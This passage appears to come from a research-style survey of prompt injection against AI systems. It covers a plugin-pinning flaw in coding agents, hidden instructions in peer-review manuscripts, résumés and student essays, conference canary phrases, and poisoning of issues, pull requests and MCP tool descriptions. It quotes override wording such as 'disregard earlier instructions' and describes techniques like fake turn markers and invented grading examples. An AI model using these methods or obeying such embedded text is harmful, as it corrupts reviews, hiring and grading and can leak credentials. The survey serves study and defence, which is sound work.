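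A marketplace can "pin" a plugin to one saved version to prevent it from changing after review. Each version has a long identifier calculated from its contents. The four agents requested the pinned version from the version-control program git, but none checked that it had received that version. In three of them, git could interpret the identifier as the name of a branch, a separate line of development that the plugin's owner can change. Gemini CLI had a different fault with the same result. An attacker who controlled the plugin's repository could therefore substitute other code while the pin appeared intact.

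AIR calls the attack "zero-click" because Claude Code and Codex update plugins automatically by default, so the substitute could reach people who had already installed the plugin. The branch version of the attack works only if the plugin's hosting service allows branch names that resemble identifiers. GitHub forbids such names, but Bitbucket and privately run servers may allow them. According to IlSoftware.it's *Plugin4Shell, falla zero-click negli agenti AI*, GitHub cited this ban in response, and AIR objected that Copilot also accepts plugins from other hosts.

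Help Net Security's *Zero-click RCE vulnerability hit four major AI coding agents, two remain unpatched* (2026) reports that Anthropic fixed the flaw in Claude Code 2.1.179 and OpenAI fixed it in Codex 0.146.0. Microsoft had not released a fix for Copilot. Google had retired Gemini CLI and advised users to move to Antigravity, which does not use the faulty mechanism. AIR sells its own plugin marketplace, but the vendors' fixes support its account.

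Plugin4Shell differs from prompt injection in how it can be fixed. An agent can compare the identifier of the version it received with the one it requested, and refuse to continue if they differ. This check has a definite answer and does not depend on the model's judgement. A model that never followed an injected instruction would still have been exposed to Plugin4Shell. Even perfect pinning would not stop an injection that a plugin's reviewers had overlooked, because the agent would install the approved version with the harmful text in it.

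### Insecure code

An attacker may prefer to have an agent write weak code that causes harm later. Karliner suggests that a poisoned rule file could lead an agent to choose outdated encryption, leave out a check on users' input or add code that leaks passwords. These examples are plausible, but Pillar demonstrated only the added script.

Liu and colleagues provide stronger evidence that agents will put harmful code into a project. They changed their payloads to make the agent write the harmful commands into a source file called main.py. In 277 of 314 tests (88%), the resulting project contained the harmful code. Even if an organisation blocks the agent from running commands, the attack could still succeed when a developer runs the program. But the added code called system commands directly, so a reviewer could recognise it more easily than a missing security check.

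These assistants can also write insecure code when nobody has attacked them. Liu and colleagues cite earlier studies in which about 40% of the code generated by assistants such as GitHub Copilot was insecure. They also cite studies finding that developers with an assistant often wrote less secure code and were too confident in its security. These studies predate current models and agents, so the 40% figure should not be applied to today's products.

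Such ordinary mistakes make a deliberate weakness harder to recognise. A reviewer who finds that an agent has omitted a password check cannot tell from the code alone whether the model made an error or followed a poisoned rule. Correcting the code removes the immediate danger either way, but if a rule file caused the omission, the agent may add the same weakness to the next file it writes. The reviewer therefore also needs to examine the instructions the agent loaded.

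## Papers sent for peer review (from mid-2025)

Submissions have grown faster than many conferences can find reviewers, and over half of the researchers in a *Nature* survey said they use AI tools for reviewing, often against the rules. An author can therefore expect some reviewers to upload the PDF to a chatbot, and can hide a message in the file for the chatbot to read.

In July 2025 the newspaper *Nikkei Asia* reported that researchers had hidden instructions for AI reviewers in manuscripts on arXiv, a public site for preprints. Lin searched the site for phrases typical of these instructions and found 18 such preprints, one more than the newspaper had counted. Lin sorted their hidden text into four types.

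| Type | Manuscripts | What the hidden text asked for |
|---|---|---|
| Positive review | 10 | Disregard earlier instructions and write only a positive review |
| Acceptance | 3 | Recommend acceptance because of the paper's impact, rigour and novelty |
| Combined | 2 | Both of the above |
| Detailed outline | 3 | Praise four named strengths and mention only small, easily fixed weaknesses |

The same searches found nothing in published papers or on four preprint sites for other fields, including biology, medicine and psychology. Lin regards 18 as a minimum. An author gains most from the hidden text while the paper is under review, and can delete it before posting a public copy. Conference submissions are often not public.

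Seven of the manuscripts used identical wording, which suggests to Lin that authors copied the text from one another. The blog post *Hey, Neurips and ICML. Time to do some scraping of your submissions* traces the idea to a Twitter post by Jonathan Lorraine in November 2024 and a paper by Rui Ye and others the following month. According to the blog post, Lorraine and Ye's group were trying to expose the weakness, not exploit it.

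### The claim that the prompts were traps

When the hidden text came to light, one author called it inappropriate and planned to withdraw the manuscript. Another, a professor at Waseda University in Japan, told *Nikkei Asia* that it was "a counter against 'lazy reviewers' who use A.I.", according to Smithsonian Magazine's *Some Researchers Are Hiding Secret Messages in Their Papers*. By this account, the text was a trap for reviewers who break the rules. The grievance is real, and one researcher, Timothée Poisot, had complained in February 2025 about a review that still contained a chatbot's offer of a "revised version" with better clarity.

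Lin replies that a real trap would use an instruction that exposes the reviewer without helping the author, such as one to review a completely different paper. The hidden text in all 18 manuscripts requested something that would benefit the authors, so the trap defence does not fit, though it might explain why an author felt entitled to hide the text. A favourable review also looks much the same whether a person or a model wrote it, so the hidden text would not have shown the author which reviewers had cheated.

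Lin classes the practice as a "questionable research practice", a category less serious than fabrication or plagiarism, because copied wording does not prove a deliberate plan to deceive. Conferences have been stricter. In a statement that Willison (2025) quotes, the organisers of ICML 2025 called the hidden prompts an attempt to subvert peer review. They compared them to bribery, where an author who offers a bribe is guilty even though the reviewer is not supposed to accept it. They added that hidden prompts meant to detect AI use by reviewers were acceptable. ICLR, another large machine-learning conference, now classes hidden instructions to language models as research misconduct.

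The commentary *LLM Usage and Manipulation in Peer Review* (Blog of the APA, 2025) spreads the blame among authors, reviewers and editors. It was written after an exchange between its writer and one of the authors involved. The two agreed that the remedy was better support and incentives for reviewers.

### Crude prompts and designed ones

Collu, Salviati and colleagues (2025), in *Publish to Perish*, tested whether the hidden text worked, which neither the press reports nor Lin's search had established. They added the five wordings found on arXiv to two papers that ICLR had rejected. They then uploaded each file to ChatGPT (GPT-4o) and asked for a review ten times with each of four requests. The requests came from a professor and three doctoral students, who had written down what they would type if they had no time to do the review themselves. The five wordings had no measurable effect on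 the ratings.

Part of the explanation is that GPT-4o's ratings were already high. In an earlier trial, it gave the two unaltered papers average ratings of 8.3 and 8 out of 10. Collu and colleagues still obtained higher ratings with two prompts of their own. One presented a high score as the reviewer's own preference, and the other gave the model the role of a reviewer who wanted to accept the paper. Neither included a command to disregard the model's instructions.

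| Model | Rejected papers tested | Average rating, unaltered | With the "preference" prompt | With the "role" prompt |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 26 | 7.93 | 9.79 | 9.01 |
| o3 | 2 | 6.40 | 9.39 | 8.22 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 2 | 7.23 | 7.78 | 8.19 |

The designed prompts also began with an imitation of the marker that opens a user's turn. To measure its effect, Collu and colleagues used a different hidden instruction, which asked GPT-4o to replace certain letters with identical-looking Cyrillic ones. GPT-4o complied in 90% of reviews of one paper and 95% of the other with the marker, compared with 0% and 5% without it. They did not repeat this comparison for the prompts that asked for high ratings, so it is uncertain how much the marker contributed to those results. The smaller effect on Gemini may also be only because they had not found the right imitation for it.

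Collu and colleagues conclude that the prompts found on arXiv "did not meaningfully affect the peer-review process". The evidence is too narrow to support this conclusion, since it comes from one model and two papers, and later tests with other models produced very different results.

The effect of hidden prompts also depends on what the reviewer asks for. When Lin explicitly asked a model for a negative review or for critical comments, the hidden prompts did not change its answer. They have more influence when a reviewer asks only for "a review", because that leaves the verdict open.

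### How favourable the reviews are without an injection

Keuper (2025), in *Prompt Injection Attacks on LLM Generated Reviews of Scientific Publications*, used a much larger sample of 1,000 randomly chosen submissions to ICLR 2024. Ten models reviewed each paper on the conference's own form, with a prompt stating that ICLR accepts fewer than 25% of papers. Keuper ran every model with no injection, with an injected sentence that called the paper very good and asked for high scores, and with one that asked for the opposite. The table shows how often some of the models gave a rating on the "accept" side of the scale. The human reviewers of the same papers did so 43% of the time.

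| Model | No injection | Favourable injection | Hostile injection |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5-mini | 54% | 100% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 85% | 100% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 94% | 100% | 0% |
| Mistral Medium | 99% | 100% | 0% |
| Llama 3.1 70B | 14% | 17% | 13% |
| DeepSeek R1 70B | 6% | 5% | 5% |

Most of the models that responded to the injection already recommended nearly every paper, so an author had little to gain from it. Keuper's hostile sentence better shows how much control an injection could have, since it cut the share of papers Gemini 2.5 Pro recommended from 94% to zero. The models that hardly reacted were also poor reviewers. DeepSeek R1 gave ratings that do not exist on the form in 70% of its reviews, and Llama did so in 56%. Keuper suggests that a model that follows instructions precisely may be easier to manipulate for that reason.

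These figures probably overstate what hidden text in a PDF would achieve. Keuper converted the papers to text and put the injected sentence before the paper, at the start of the user's message, where it could be mistaken for part of the reviewer's own request. In a separate test, hidden white and tiny text reached ChatGPT but not Google's Gemini website, which apparently read pages as images. But Collu and colleagues found that their white text did reach Gemini 2.5 Flash, so the result may depend on the version of the service or on the file.

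Gharami and colleagues attacked 20 ICLR papers in December 2025 and reported that ChatGPT-5.1 and Gemini mostly rated them between 6 and 8. They published no ratings for the unaltered papers, so the attack may not explain these ratings. Keuper's results show that models can give similar ratings to papers without injections.

### Tests on the models of 2026

In May 2026, Li, Xiong and colleagues tested the crude wording from arXiv on a larger scale in *LLM-as-a-Reviewer*, giving 898 papers from NeurIPS and ICLR to twelve models. They put one instruction at the start of each paper, using an altered font so that a person would see an ordinary notice. Among the papers a model had rated below 8 without the instruction, they counted how many it rated 8 or higher with it. The ranges cover NeurIPS 2022, ICLR 2023 and ICLR 2025.

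| Model | Low-rated papers raised to 8 or higher |
|---|---|
| Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | 63–71% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 63–69% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 26–94% |
| Qwen3.5-9B | 25–68% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0–8% |
| GPT-5.4 | 0–5% |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 0% |

GPT-5.4 is a strict reviewer, so a paper's rating might need a large increase to reach 8. But its ratings rose for only 7% to 13% of the low-rated papers, which suggests that it mostly ignored the instruction. Gemini 3 Flash behaved differently despite being released only about three months earlier, so a model's release date is a poor guide to whether it resists. Li and colleagues tested only the smaller models from Google and Anthropic, and no models released after May 2026.

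In further tests on Gemini 3 Flash, repeating the instruction up to nine times did not consistently make it more effective. Moving it to the end of the paper did, and 87% of the low-rated papers then scored 8 or higher. Wording had the largest effect. Because the main results cover only one sentence in one position, GPT-5.4 might not resist a more effective sentence even though it resisted that one.

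Unlike Li and colleagues, *Does AI Reviewer See the Full Picture?* (June 2026) finds commercial models more susceptible than open ones. Larger models are also often more susceptible, while some small ones are unaffected only because they fail to write a usable review, much as Keuper had observed. Li and colleagues used a plain order, whereas the June study disguised its instructions, for example by encoding them, to get past commercial models' safety filters. A model could easily resist one of these attacks but follow the other. The June study also raised ratings by making imperceptible changes to a paper's figures, which no check of the text would find.

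Keuper's finding that models are lenient no longer holds for all models. Llama 3.3 70B rated the papers 1.5 to 2.4 points higher than the human reviewers did, but GPT-5.4 rated the ICLR papers about half a point lower than they did.

An author may not need an injection to benefit from a lenient AI reviewer. *Stop Automating Peer Review Without Rigorous Evaluation* (2026) describes "paper laundering", in which the author asks a language model to rewrite the paper once, without adding hidden text or tuning the paper against the reviewer. The rewrite raised AI reviewers' scores. Paper laundering breaks no current conference rule, since authors may use AI to improve their writing, and a search for hidden instructions would not detect it.

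### Random phrases as a test for AI-written reviews

Conference organisers can also alter the PDF before they send it to reviewers. *Detecting LLM-Generated Peer Reviews* (Rao, Kumar and colleagues, 2025) describes how they could use hidden text to catch reviewers who break a ban on AI. The organisers hide an instruction in the PDF that tells an AI model to include a particular phrase in its review, then search the submitted reviews for that phrase.

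The method must avoid accusing an honest reviewer who happens to use the phrase. Ordinary detectors of AI text look for a style that models favour, so they may repeatedly accuse a person who naturally writes that way. Rao and colleagues instead have the organisers draw the phrase at random from a long list, separately for each paper. Because the draw does not depend on how anyone writes, it limits the risk of a false accusation whatever the reviewer's style.

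Suppose the list has 100,000 phrases and a reviewer, writing unaided, uses one of them. The chance that it is the phrase drawn for that paper is 1 in 100,000. The organisers add up these chances for the whole conference. If all the human-written reviews together contain 50 uses of listed phrases, the chance of even one false accusation is at most 50 ÷ 100,000, or 0.05%. If the total is too high, the organisers leave out the most common phrases, or the reviews with the most listed phrases, before they look at which phrase belongs to which paper.

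In tests on 100 ICLR papers, the most reliable marker phrase was an invented citation with a random surname and year. When the instruction to include it was hidden in the PDF as white text, the models of the time did so in 98.6% of reviews on average. More than 94% of marked reviews kept their marker after another model paraphrased them. Lin cites the 98.6% as evidence that hidden instructions are highly effective, but it measures only how often models inserted a harmless phrase, not how often they obeyed demands for praise.

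### ICML 2026

ICML used the method on a large scale in 2026. *On Violations of LLM Review Policies* (Agarwal, Dudik and colleagues, 2026), the organisers' own account, describes the conference's two policies. Policy A banned any use of language models in reviewing, while Policy B let reviewers use them to understand a paper and polish the review. Every reviewer under Policy A had either chosen it or said that both were acceptable. ICML had also warned reviewers that it might reject all their own papers if they failed in their duties.

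The organisers compiled a list of 170,000 phrases, drew two at random for each paper, and hid an instruction in the PDF to include both in the review. There are about 14 billion possible pairs. A human reviewer does not choose one pair out of 14 billion, however, because a long review may contain several phrases from the list. If it contains *m* of the *N* phrases, the chance that both of the drawn phrases are among them is

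*m*(*m* − 1) ÷ *N*(*N* − 1)

For a review that contains ten of the 170,000 phrases, the probability of a coincidental match is 90 ÷ 28.9 billion, or about 1 in 320 million. Agarwal and colleagues put the chance of wrongly flagging even one review under Policy A at 0.0001. This estimate covers only coincidental matches, but a reviewer might also quote the phrases to report the hidden text, so a person checked every flagged review.

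The search flagged 795 reviews by 506 reviewers, all under Policy A. ICML deleted the reviews and removed 51 people from its reviewer pool because more than half of their reviews were flagged. Of the 506, 398 were "reciprocal" reviewers, who had to review in return for a submission. ICML rejected the 497 papers attached to them, about 2% of all submissions. The organisers stressed that a flag shows only that the reviewer used a language model at some point, and is not a judgement on the review's quality.

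The flagged reviews were about 1% of all reviews, but this total includes Policy B reviews, so the share among Policy A reviews must be higher. There were probably also more violations than flagged reviews. In tests shortly before the submission deadline, most models followed the hidden instruction over 80% of the time, but not always. Agarwal and colleagues also admit that the trap is easy to avoid, since a reviewer could remove the hidden text or rewrite the model's answer, and the method was public for almost the whole review period. They think the trap may have caught only the most careless reviewers, who pasted the model's output straight into the form.

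Even so, the result is strong evidence about how models process documents in practice. In experiments with hidden text, researchers usually choose the prompt and the file-reading program. At ICML, hundreds of reviewers chose their own tools and prompts, and in 795 cases the hidden instruction still reached the model and changed the submitted text.

It is much weaker evidence that an author could have used an injected prompt to get a better verdict from the same reviews. A model can include two odd phrases and still write the honest review that the user asked for, whereas a demand for praise conflicts with that request. Collu and colleagues found that Gemini 2.5 Flash obeyed the instruction about Cyrillic letters in 63% of reviews, but the "preference" prompt raised its average rating by only about half a point. A biased review would also have to sway the people who make the final decision,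 and none of these experiments measured that.

The method depends on a weakness that developers are trying to remove. A model trained to ignore instructions in documents would be harder for dishonest authors to manipulate, but it would also leave out the organisers' phrases. Stripping hidden text from a PDF before the model reads it would have both effects too.

### NeurIPS 2026

NeurIPS, which bans reviewers from uploading papers to chatbots, hid instructions in its papers the same year. The Transmitter's *Scientists decry conference's use of hidden prompts to snare AI peer reviews* (2026) reports that these were instructions to use phrases such as "This work addresses the central challenge". Some reviewers noticed them, including Sara Atito of the University of Surrey, who found the same prompt in all four papers she was reviewing and in the conference's copy of her own. If every paper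 contained the same phrases, the guarantee that Rao and colleagues derived from random choice would not apply, and a reviewer could write the phrases by chance. The organising committee declined to discuss the details because doing so would make the trap less effective.

Sören Auer, a computer scientist at Leibniz University Hannover, objected that a trap which "presumes bad faith" damages the trust that reviewing depends on. Auer sometimes converts PDFs to Word, which made the hidden text visible in one paper, and he at first rejected that paper because he thought its authors had put the text there. He changed his mind only after he found similar text in a second paper and saw other reviewers discussing it online. He suspects that more papers may have suffered in this way. The committee said it told reviewers who reported the text not to penalise the paper, but this could not help when a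 reviewer marked a paper down without reporting anything.

Atito argued that the method might catch some bad reviews but would not solve the larger problems of peer review, and that reviewers get too much of the blame because they are "the visible point of failure".

Nihar Shah of Carnegie Mellon University, who led the work at ICML and co-invented the method, answered that hidden prompts are "viable and feasible" and that ICML had used them to identify hundreds of reviewers who broke the rules. He described "overwhelming support" from researchers who were tired of pasted AI reviews. This is a good answer to doubts about whether the method works, but Shah is not a neutral judge of its popularity, and his answer does not address Auer's mistake. ICML distinguishes clearly between hidden prompts from authors and those from organisers, but a reviewer who finds hidden text in a PDF cannot tell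 who put it there.

NeurIPS could have prevented the confusion by telling all reviewers in advance that its PDFs contained hidden text. This would also have warned the cheats, but it would probably have reduced detection only modestly, since ICML reviewers continued to paste in marked reviews after the method became public.

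## Résumés, student essays and other scored documents

Job applicants and students have much the same incentive as researchers who submit papers, because a better score from an AI system can bring an interview or a higher grade. They usually submit a document once and see only the result, so they have little chance to improve a payload by trial and error. *Measuring Real-World Prompt Injection Attacks in LLM-based Resume Screening* (Zhang, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) searched 196,682 real résumés from the recruitment platform hireEZ and found that about 1% contained hidden text apparently meant to influence screening software.

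### Counting hidden text in résumés

The résumés came from two sources, with similar results.

| Source | Period | Résumés | With hidden text | Of these, no explicit instruction |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| hireEZ's own matching product | July 2024 to November 2025 | 83,277 | 993 (1.19%) | 90.5% |
| Employers' applicant-tracking systems | July 2019 to December 2025 | 113,405 | 1,037 (0.91%) | 95.7% |

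Zhang and colleagues built two detectors that use GPT-5. The first applies fixed rules to find type smaller than 4 points, letters close to the background colour, and text that leaves almost no mark when the page is rendered. These rules flag about 2% of résumés. GPT-5 then classifies only the flagged passages as deliberately hidden or not. The second detector gives GPT-5 images of the pages along with the extracted text, and prompts it to identify what appears only in the text.

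Murray's PhantomLint would skip a hidden list of programming languages, because it checks only passages that resemble typical injection phrases.

To validate the detectors, the researchers ran both on 62,029 résumés and checked some of the results by hand.

| Flagged by | Résumés | Checked | Confirmed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Both detectors | 517 | 100 | 100 |
| Rule-based detector only | 276 | 100 | 60 |
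| Picture comparison only | 85 | 85 | 41 |
| Neither | 61,151 | 100 | 0 |

From these samples, Zhang and colleagues estimate that 86% of the rule-based detector's alarms and 93% of the picture comparison's are correct. The rule-based detector raised false alarms about decorative text and leftover watermark fragments, while the picture comparison sometimes reported visible text as hidden. The researchers used the rule-based detector for the full count because it cost about $20 to run, while the picture comparison would have cost an estimated $2,680.

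The researchers call the resulting 1% a conservative lower bound, which is doubtful because the share falls to about 0.9% if 14% of the alarms are false. The detector also misses some hidden text, but the sample of 100 unflagged résumés is too small to show how much. Finding none in 100 is compatible with a true rate of up to about 3%, three times the rate they measured. "Roughly 1%" is a fair summary, with some uncertainty in both directions.

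Zhang and colleagues' figures show that hidden injections peaked in 2024, although they state in their abstract that such injections have become noticeably more common over the past one to two years. In the employers' systems, the share stayed between 0.6% and 0.8% from 2019 to 2023, reached about 1.2% in 2024 and fell to 0.67% in the second half of 2025. In hireEZ's own product, it fell from about 1.5% to 1.0%.

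Kingery (2026), in *Thwarting Hidden Resume Hacks Targeting AI Hiring Tools*, an article from Duke University, reports that the number of résumés with hidden text still rose sevenfold between July 2024 and November 2025. Since the share of résumés with hidden text fell by about a third over that period, the total number of résumés must have grown roughly tenfold.

### Hidden skills and copied job descriptions

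More than 90% of the hidden passages contained no instruction. Most were lists of skills, and others described work experience, named a qualification or repeated the requirements of the job advertisement. Zhang and colleagues call this "data injection" and count it as prompt injection. Under the narrower and more usual definition, which requires an injected instruction, only about 139 of the résumés qualify, or one in 1,400. About 60% of those combined several tricks, such as telling the model to disregard its instructions and declaring the applicant highly qualified. None contained the meaningless strings of characters that researchers generate by computer to attack a particular model.

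A command is meant to replace the screening task, while a hidden skill supplies false evidence for it. For example, an applicant who has never used Python might add the word in white type when a job requires it. Screening software typically sorts a résumé into fields for skills, experience and education before comparing it with the job. "Python" goes into the skills field with the applicant's real skills and counts as a match. A sentence demanding an interview fits none of these fields, so the software may discard it. Zhang and colleagues suggest this is one reason applicants prefer keywords to commands.

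Copying the job description into a résumé works in a similar way. The copied text contains no information about the applicant, but software that compares résumés with the advertisement will rate the résumé as a close match.

Neither trick requires a language model. Zhang and colleagues found hidden keywords in résumés from 2019, when employers mostly used conventional keyword search. Much of the 1% is therefore probably an older form of cheating that also works on newer systems.

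Whether hidden text gives a command or lists a skill affects which defences help. Training a model to ignore commands in documents does not teach it to discount a listed skill. Filters that read only the text did badly in a test with 10,000 résumés, 100 of which had confirmed hidden text. Meta's Prompt Guard caught five of the 100, PromptArmor caught seven, and Data Sentinel caught 87 but also flagged nearly all the other résumés. Removing hidden text works much better. The applicant then has to claim the skill in visible type, where a recruiter can question it.

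Zhang and colleagues did not test whether the hidden text changed anyone's chances. Their data did not include hiring decisions, and they chose not to experiment on live systems. Kingery quotes one of the researchers, Neil Gong, as saying that a few years ago such attacks "would have been completely effective", but the study contains no evidence for this. Another of the researchers, Tianlong Chen, told Kingery that some applicants may have used a template without knowing that it contained hidden text. Chen was hireEZ's chief AI scientist when the company collected the data. hireEZ now uses both detectors in its products, but people make the final screening decisions.

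### Self-promotion in a pool of ten

Baxi, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *Prompt Injection in Automated Résumé Screening with Large Language Models*, used invented résumés to measure how much an added sentence helps a candidate. They asked two models to rank ten candidates for an IT support job, and added a sentence to one résumé without adding any qualifications. In some rounds the sentence praised the candidate as exceptionally well qualified, and in others it was a command to place the candidate above everyone else.

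In the first pool, all ten candidates had five years of experience. In the second, half had ten years and half had five. The table shows the average number of places gained and, in brackets, how often the candidate moved up.

| Pool and candidate | Model | Praise | Command |
|---|---|---|---|
| Equal pool | DeepSeek-V3.2 | 4.2 (86%) | 4.1 (85%) |
| Equal pool | GPT-4o-mini | 0.6 (7%) | 2.4 (60%) |
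| Mixed pool, more experienced | DeepSeek-V3.2 | 1.5 (59%) | 2.0 (79%) |
| Mixed pool, less experienced | DeepSeek-V3.2 | 3.0 (41%) | 6.5 (93%) |
| Mixed pool, more experienced | GPT-4o-mini | 0.1 (14%) | 1.0 (49%) |
| Mixed pool, less experienced | GPT-4o-mini | 0.0 (7%) | 2.6 (46%) |

A gain of 4.2 places is close to the maximum average gain of 4.5. Ten equal candidates in random order have an average position of 5.5, and a candidate whom the model always puts first moves from there to 1. One candidate in ten already starts first and cannot move up, so the success rate cannot exceed 90%. DeepSeek must therefore have put the self-promoting candidate at or near the top almost every time.

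Baxi and colleagues conclude that manipulation is less effective on average when candidates differ in quality, though a weaker candidate can "occasionally" outrank a stronger one. That conclusion fits the results for praise but understates the effect of the command on DeepSeek. If DeepSeek normally ranks the five experienced candidates first, the other five average position 8. A gain of 6.5 places then moves a less experienced candidate to about position 1.5, ahead of nearly all the experienced ones.

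The advantage shrinks as more candidates use the trick, because only one of them can be first. Suppose the ten equal candidates are ranked A to J. If F adds the sentence and the model moves F to the top, F gains five places and A to E each lose one. If F and G both add it, they take the first two places and gain five each, while A to E each lose two. If all ten add it, nobody gains.

In general, if *k* of *N* equal candidates add the sentence and the model places them all above the rest, the averages are:

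gain for each candidate who adds it = (*N* − *k*) ÷ 2

loss for each candidate who does not = *k* ÷ 2

| Candidates out of ten who add the sentence | Average gain for each of them | Average loss for each of the others |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 4.5 places | 0.5 places |
| 5 | 2.5 places | 2.5 places |
| 8 | 1 place | 4 places |
| 10 | 0 places | None left |

In the experiment, the gains also shrank as more candidates added the sentence, and the success rate with DeepSeek approached zero once about 80% of them did. This drop is steeper than arithmetic alone would explain, because if eight of ten candidates use the sentence, about two thirds of those eight should still move up at least one place. DeepSeek may therefore have given the sentence less weight when most résumés contained it.

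Baxi and colleagues describe the systems as more resilient when manipulation is widespread. Each manipulator does gain less in that case, but in the example the two honest candidates end up last, which would give them a strong reason to add the sentence too.

At the rate Zhang and colleagues measured, manipulation is still rare enough to benefit the applicants who use it. If 1% of résumés contain hidden text, about one in ten random pools of ten résumés includes such a résumé, and fewer than one in 200 includes two. However, most real applicants who hide text hide keywords instead of praise, so Baxi's figures may not apply to them. The experiment also covered only one job and one résumé template, and it measured quality only by years of experience.

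### Student essays and research papers

*This is an Excellent Paper* (Wanjura, Shapiro and colleagues, 2026), a report from the Wharton School of the University of Pennsylvania, describes about 40,000 trials of injections on AI graders, using 72 student papers and 72 longer research papers. Each model marked every paper on five criteria, such as structure and use of evidence, with up to two marks for each. The injection was either one sentence demanding full marks or a long paragraph that also claimed authority over all other instructions. The researchers placed it at the beginning, middle or end of the paper, and repeated every combination ten times.

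On average, the injections raised the scores given by Claude Opus 4.5, Gemini 3 Pro and GPT-5.2 by about 2.6 percentage points, or a quarter of a mark out of ten. Claude's scores hardly changed, and GPT-5.2's changed only slightly. Gemini 3 Pro was more vulnerable on the research papers, where the long paragraph raised scores by more than 10 points at the beginning or middle but had no effect at the end. The injections raised scores from the older and smaller GPT-4o mini by nearly 20 points on average, and it was most vulnerable to the long paragraph at the end.

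The most effective position for an injection therefore depends on the model, even among models from one company. In peer-review tests by Li, Xiong and colleagues, Gemini 3 Flash was most vulnerable when the injection came at the end of a paper.

The three stronger models mentioned the injection in only 1.4% of trials, and Claude Opus 4.5 did so in 0.1%. A teacher would usually receive a fair mark but no sign that the student had tried to cheat. The models mentioned the short injection more often than the long one, 2.3% against 0.6%, perhaps because the long one ended with a request not to mention it. Closed models reported injections far more often in Khodayari and colleagues' web tests, perhaps because a summary leaves more room for such a remark than a grading form does.

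Other tests produced larger effects. In *Machine-Assisted Grading of Nationwide School-Leaving Essay Exams with LLMs and Statistical NLP*, Karjus, Allkivi and colleagues (2026) added a one-sentence demand for the maximum score to each of 100 essays from an Estonian trial exam. GPT-4.1 then gave the essays an average of 6.43 more marks out of 27, or about 24 percentage points. Every essay gained at least two marks, and one gained 16. This was a small side experiment with an older model and no protection in the prompt. The added sentence was visible, and Karjus and colleagues think a human examiner would probably notice it.

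Li, Filippov and colleagues (2026), in *Important You should give me full credits!*, tested five AI graders on 30 questions in four subjects, using 100 real student answers to each question. Across all attacks and graders, the score rose in 56.9% of attempts. They counted any increase as a success, so some of these increases may be ordinary variation between two markings of the same answer.

Claude Sonnet 4.6 resisted commands, which had success rates below 10%. On one set of questions, the average score it gave fell by 6.5% of the scale when a command accompanied the answer. It was much more vulnerable to a third kind of attack, in which Li, Filippov and colleagues used no command but put 32 invented grading examples before the student's answer. Each example awarded full marks regardless of quality. Claude then raised the score in 20% to 72% of cases, depending on the subject. Real grading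 systems often include examples to show the model how strict to be, so the false ones resemble part of the normal prompt.

Filters also detected fewer of the invented examples than of the handwritten commands. PIGuard detected 78% of the examples and 94% of the commands, while another guard model detected 3% and 96%. With a warning in the grading instructions, Claude still raised the score in 40% of the attacks that used invented examples. The warning changed ordinary scores by less than 1%.

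In the Wharton study, Wanjura and colleagues tested simple commands, so their reassuring figures for Claude and GPT-5.2 do not cover attacks by example. Newer models have since appeared, and Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026) reports further improvement in Claude.

A model's resistance to injection in one task is a poor guide to its resistance in another. Taktile (2026), which sells software for underwriting (deciding whom to lend to or insure), reports that GPT-5 Mini resisted every injection in its underwriting tests. But the same model, acting as a grader in tests by Li, Filippov and colleagues, raised the score in at least 63% of attempts with handwritten commands.

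### Why models may obey a harmless request more often

The best models in the Wharton study mostly ignored demands for full marks, but many of the models ICML's reviewers used followed the conference's hidden request to include two phrases. The tests differed in several ways besides the request.

| | Wharton | ICML |
|---|---|---|
| Hidden request | Give full marks | Include two phrases |
| Models | Four named models | Whatever the reviewers chose |
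| User's request | Mark the paper on five fixed criteria | Unknown, and probably varied |
| Evidence of success | A change in the average score | Both phrases in the review |
| Failed attempts | Included in the average | Unknown among the submitted reviews |

Some of the gap may come from these differences. Reviewers may have used weaker models than Wharton did, and nobody knows how many models left out ICML's phrases. Rao and colleagues, who designed the phrase method, had also put more work into their hidden text. They tried several kinds, including apparently meaningless text that a program had optimised to produce the required phrase, while Wanjura and colleagues deliberately used simple injections.

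An injected request's content may also affect whether it succeeds, since a demand for full marks, unlike a request to include a phrase, conflicts with the user's task. If models resist mainly because of this conflict, a payload that asks for a small change in emphasis should succeed more often than one that asks for a perfect score. The Gemini 3 Flash results from Li, Xiong and colleagues are evidence against this as a general rule, because the most effective wording was a direct demand for a positive review and a score of 10 out of 10.

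Models may also have learned to recognise typical attacks. A demand for full marks, worded to override all other instructions, resembles the attacks developers use in training, while a request to include a phrase could pass for a conference's formatting rule. But contrary to this explanation, Wharton's long paragraph, which made the strongest claim to authority, worked better than the single sentence.

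A third possibility is that detailed marking criteria leave less room for outside influence than a request for "a review", as Lin's peer-review experiments suggest. But GPT-4.1 still raised every score under Karjus and colleagues' nine-criterion marking scheme, so detailed criteria are not enough to protect a weaker model.

A better test would give the same model the same essays, with the hidden instruction in the same place, and change only whether that instruction was to include a phrase, raise the score or lower it. Collu and colleagues came closest to this in their peer-review tests. GPT-4o followed both a harmless instruction and instructions to give a better rating, while Gemini 2.5 Flash usually followed the harmless one but raised its ratings only slightly.

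## Issues, pull requests and other metadata (from late 2025)

In software projects, users report problems in issues, contributors propose changes in pull requests, and programs produce error messages and logs. Many projects now use agents to sort, review and answer this material, so outsiders can get text to an agent without having a file accepted into the project. From late 2025, security researchers showed that such text could make agents publish the credentials they had been given for their work.

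| Text | Who can write it | Which agent usually reads it |
|---|---|---|
| Issue titles, issue bodies and comments | Anyone with an account, on most public projects | The project's triage agent, which labels and sorts new issues |
| Pull request titles and descriptions | Anyone who proposes a change | The project's review agent |
| Commit messages and branch names | The author of the change | Review agents, and agents that draft release notes |
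| Error messages and test logs | The author of the code that failed | Agents that repair failed builds |
| Package descriptions | The package's publisher | A coding agent that looks for software to install |
| Tool descriptions | Whoever runs the tool server | Every agent connected to that server |

### Tool descriptions

The Model Context Protocol (MCP), which Anthropic introduced in November 2024, is a standard way to connect models to outside tools. A program called an MCP server provides the tools, along with written descriptions of what each one does and when to use it. The user's application, called the client, puts these descriptions in the model's context window. Whoever runs the server can add instructions to a description, an attack known as tool poisoning. They can also supply a harmless description at first and change it after the user has approved the tool.

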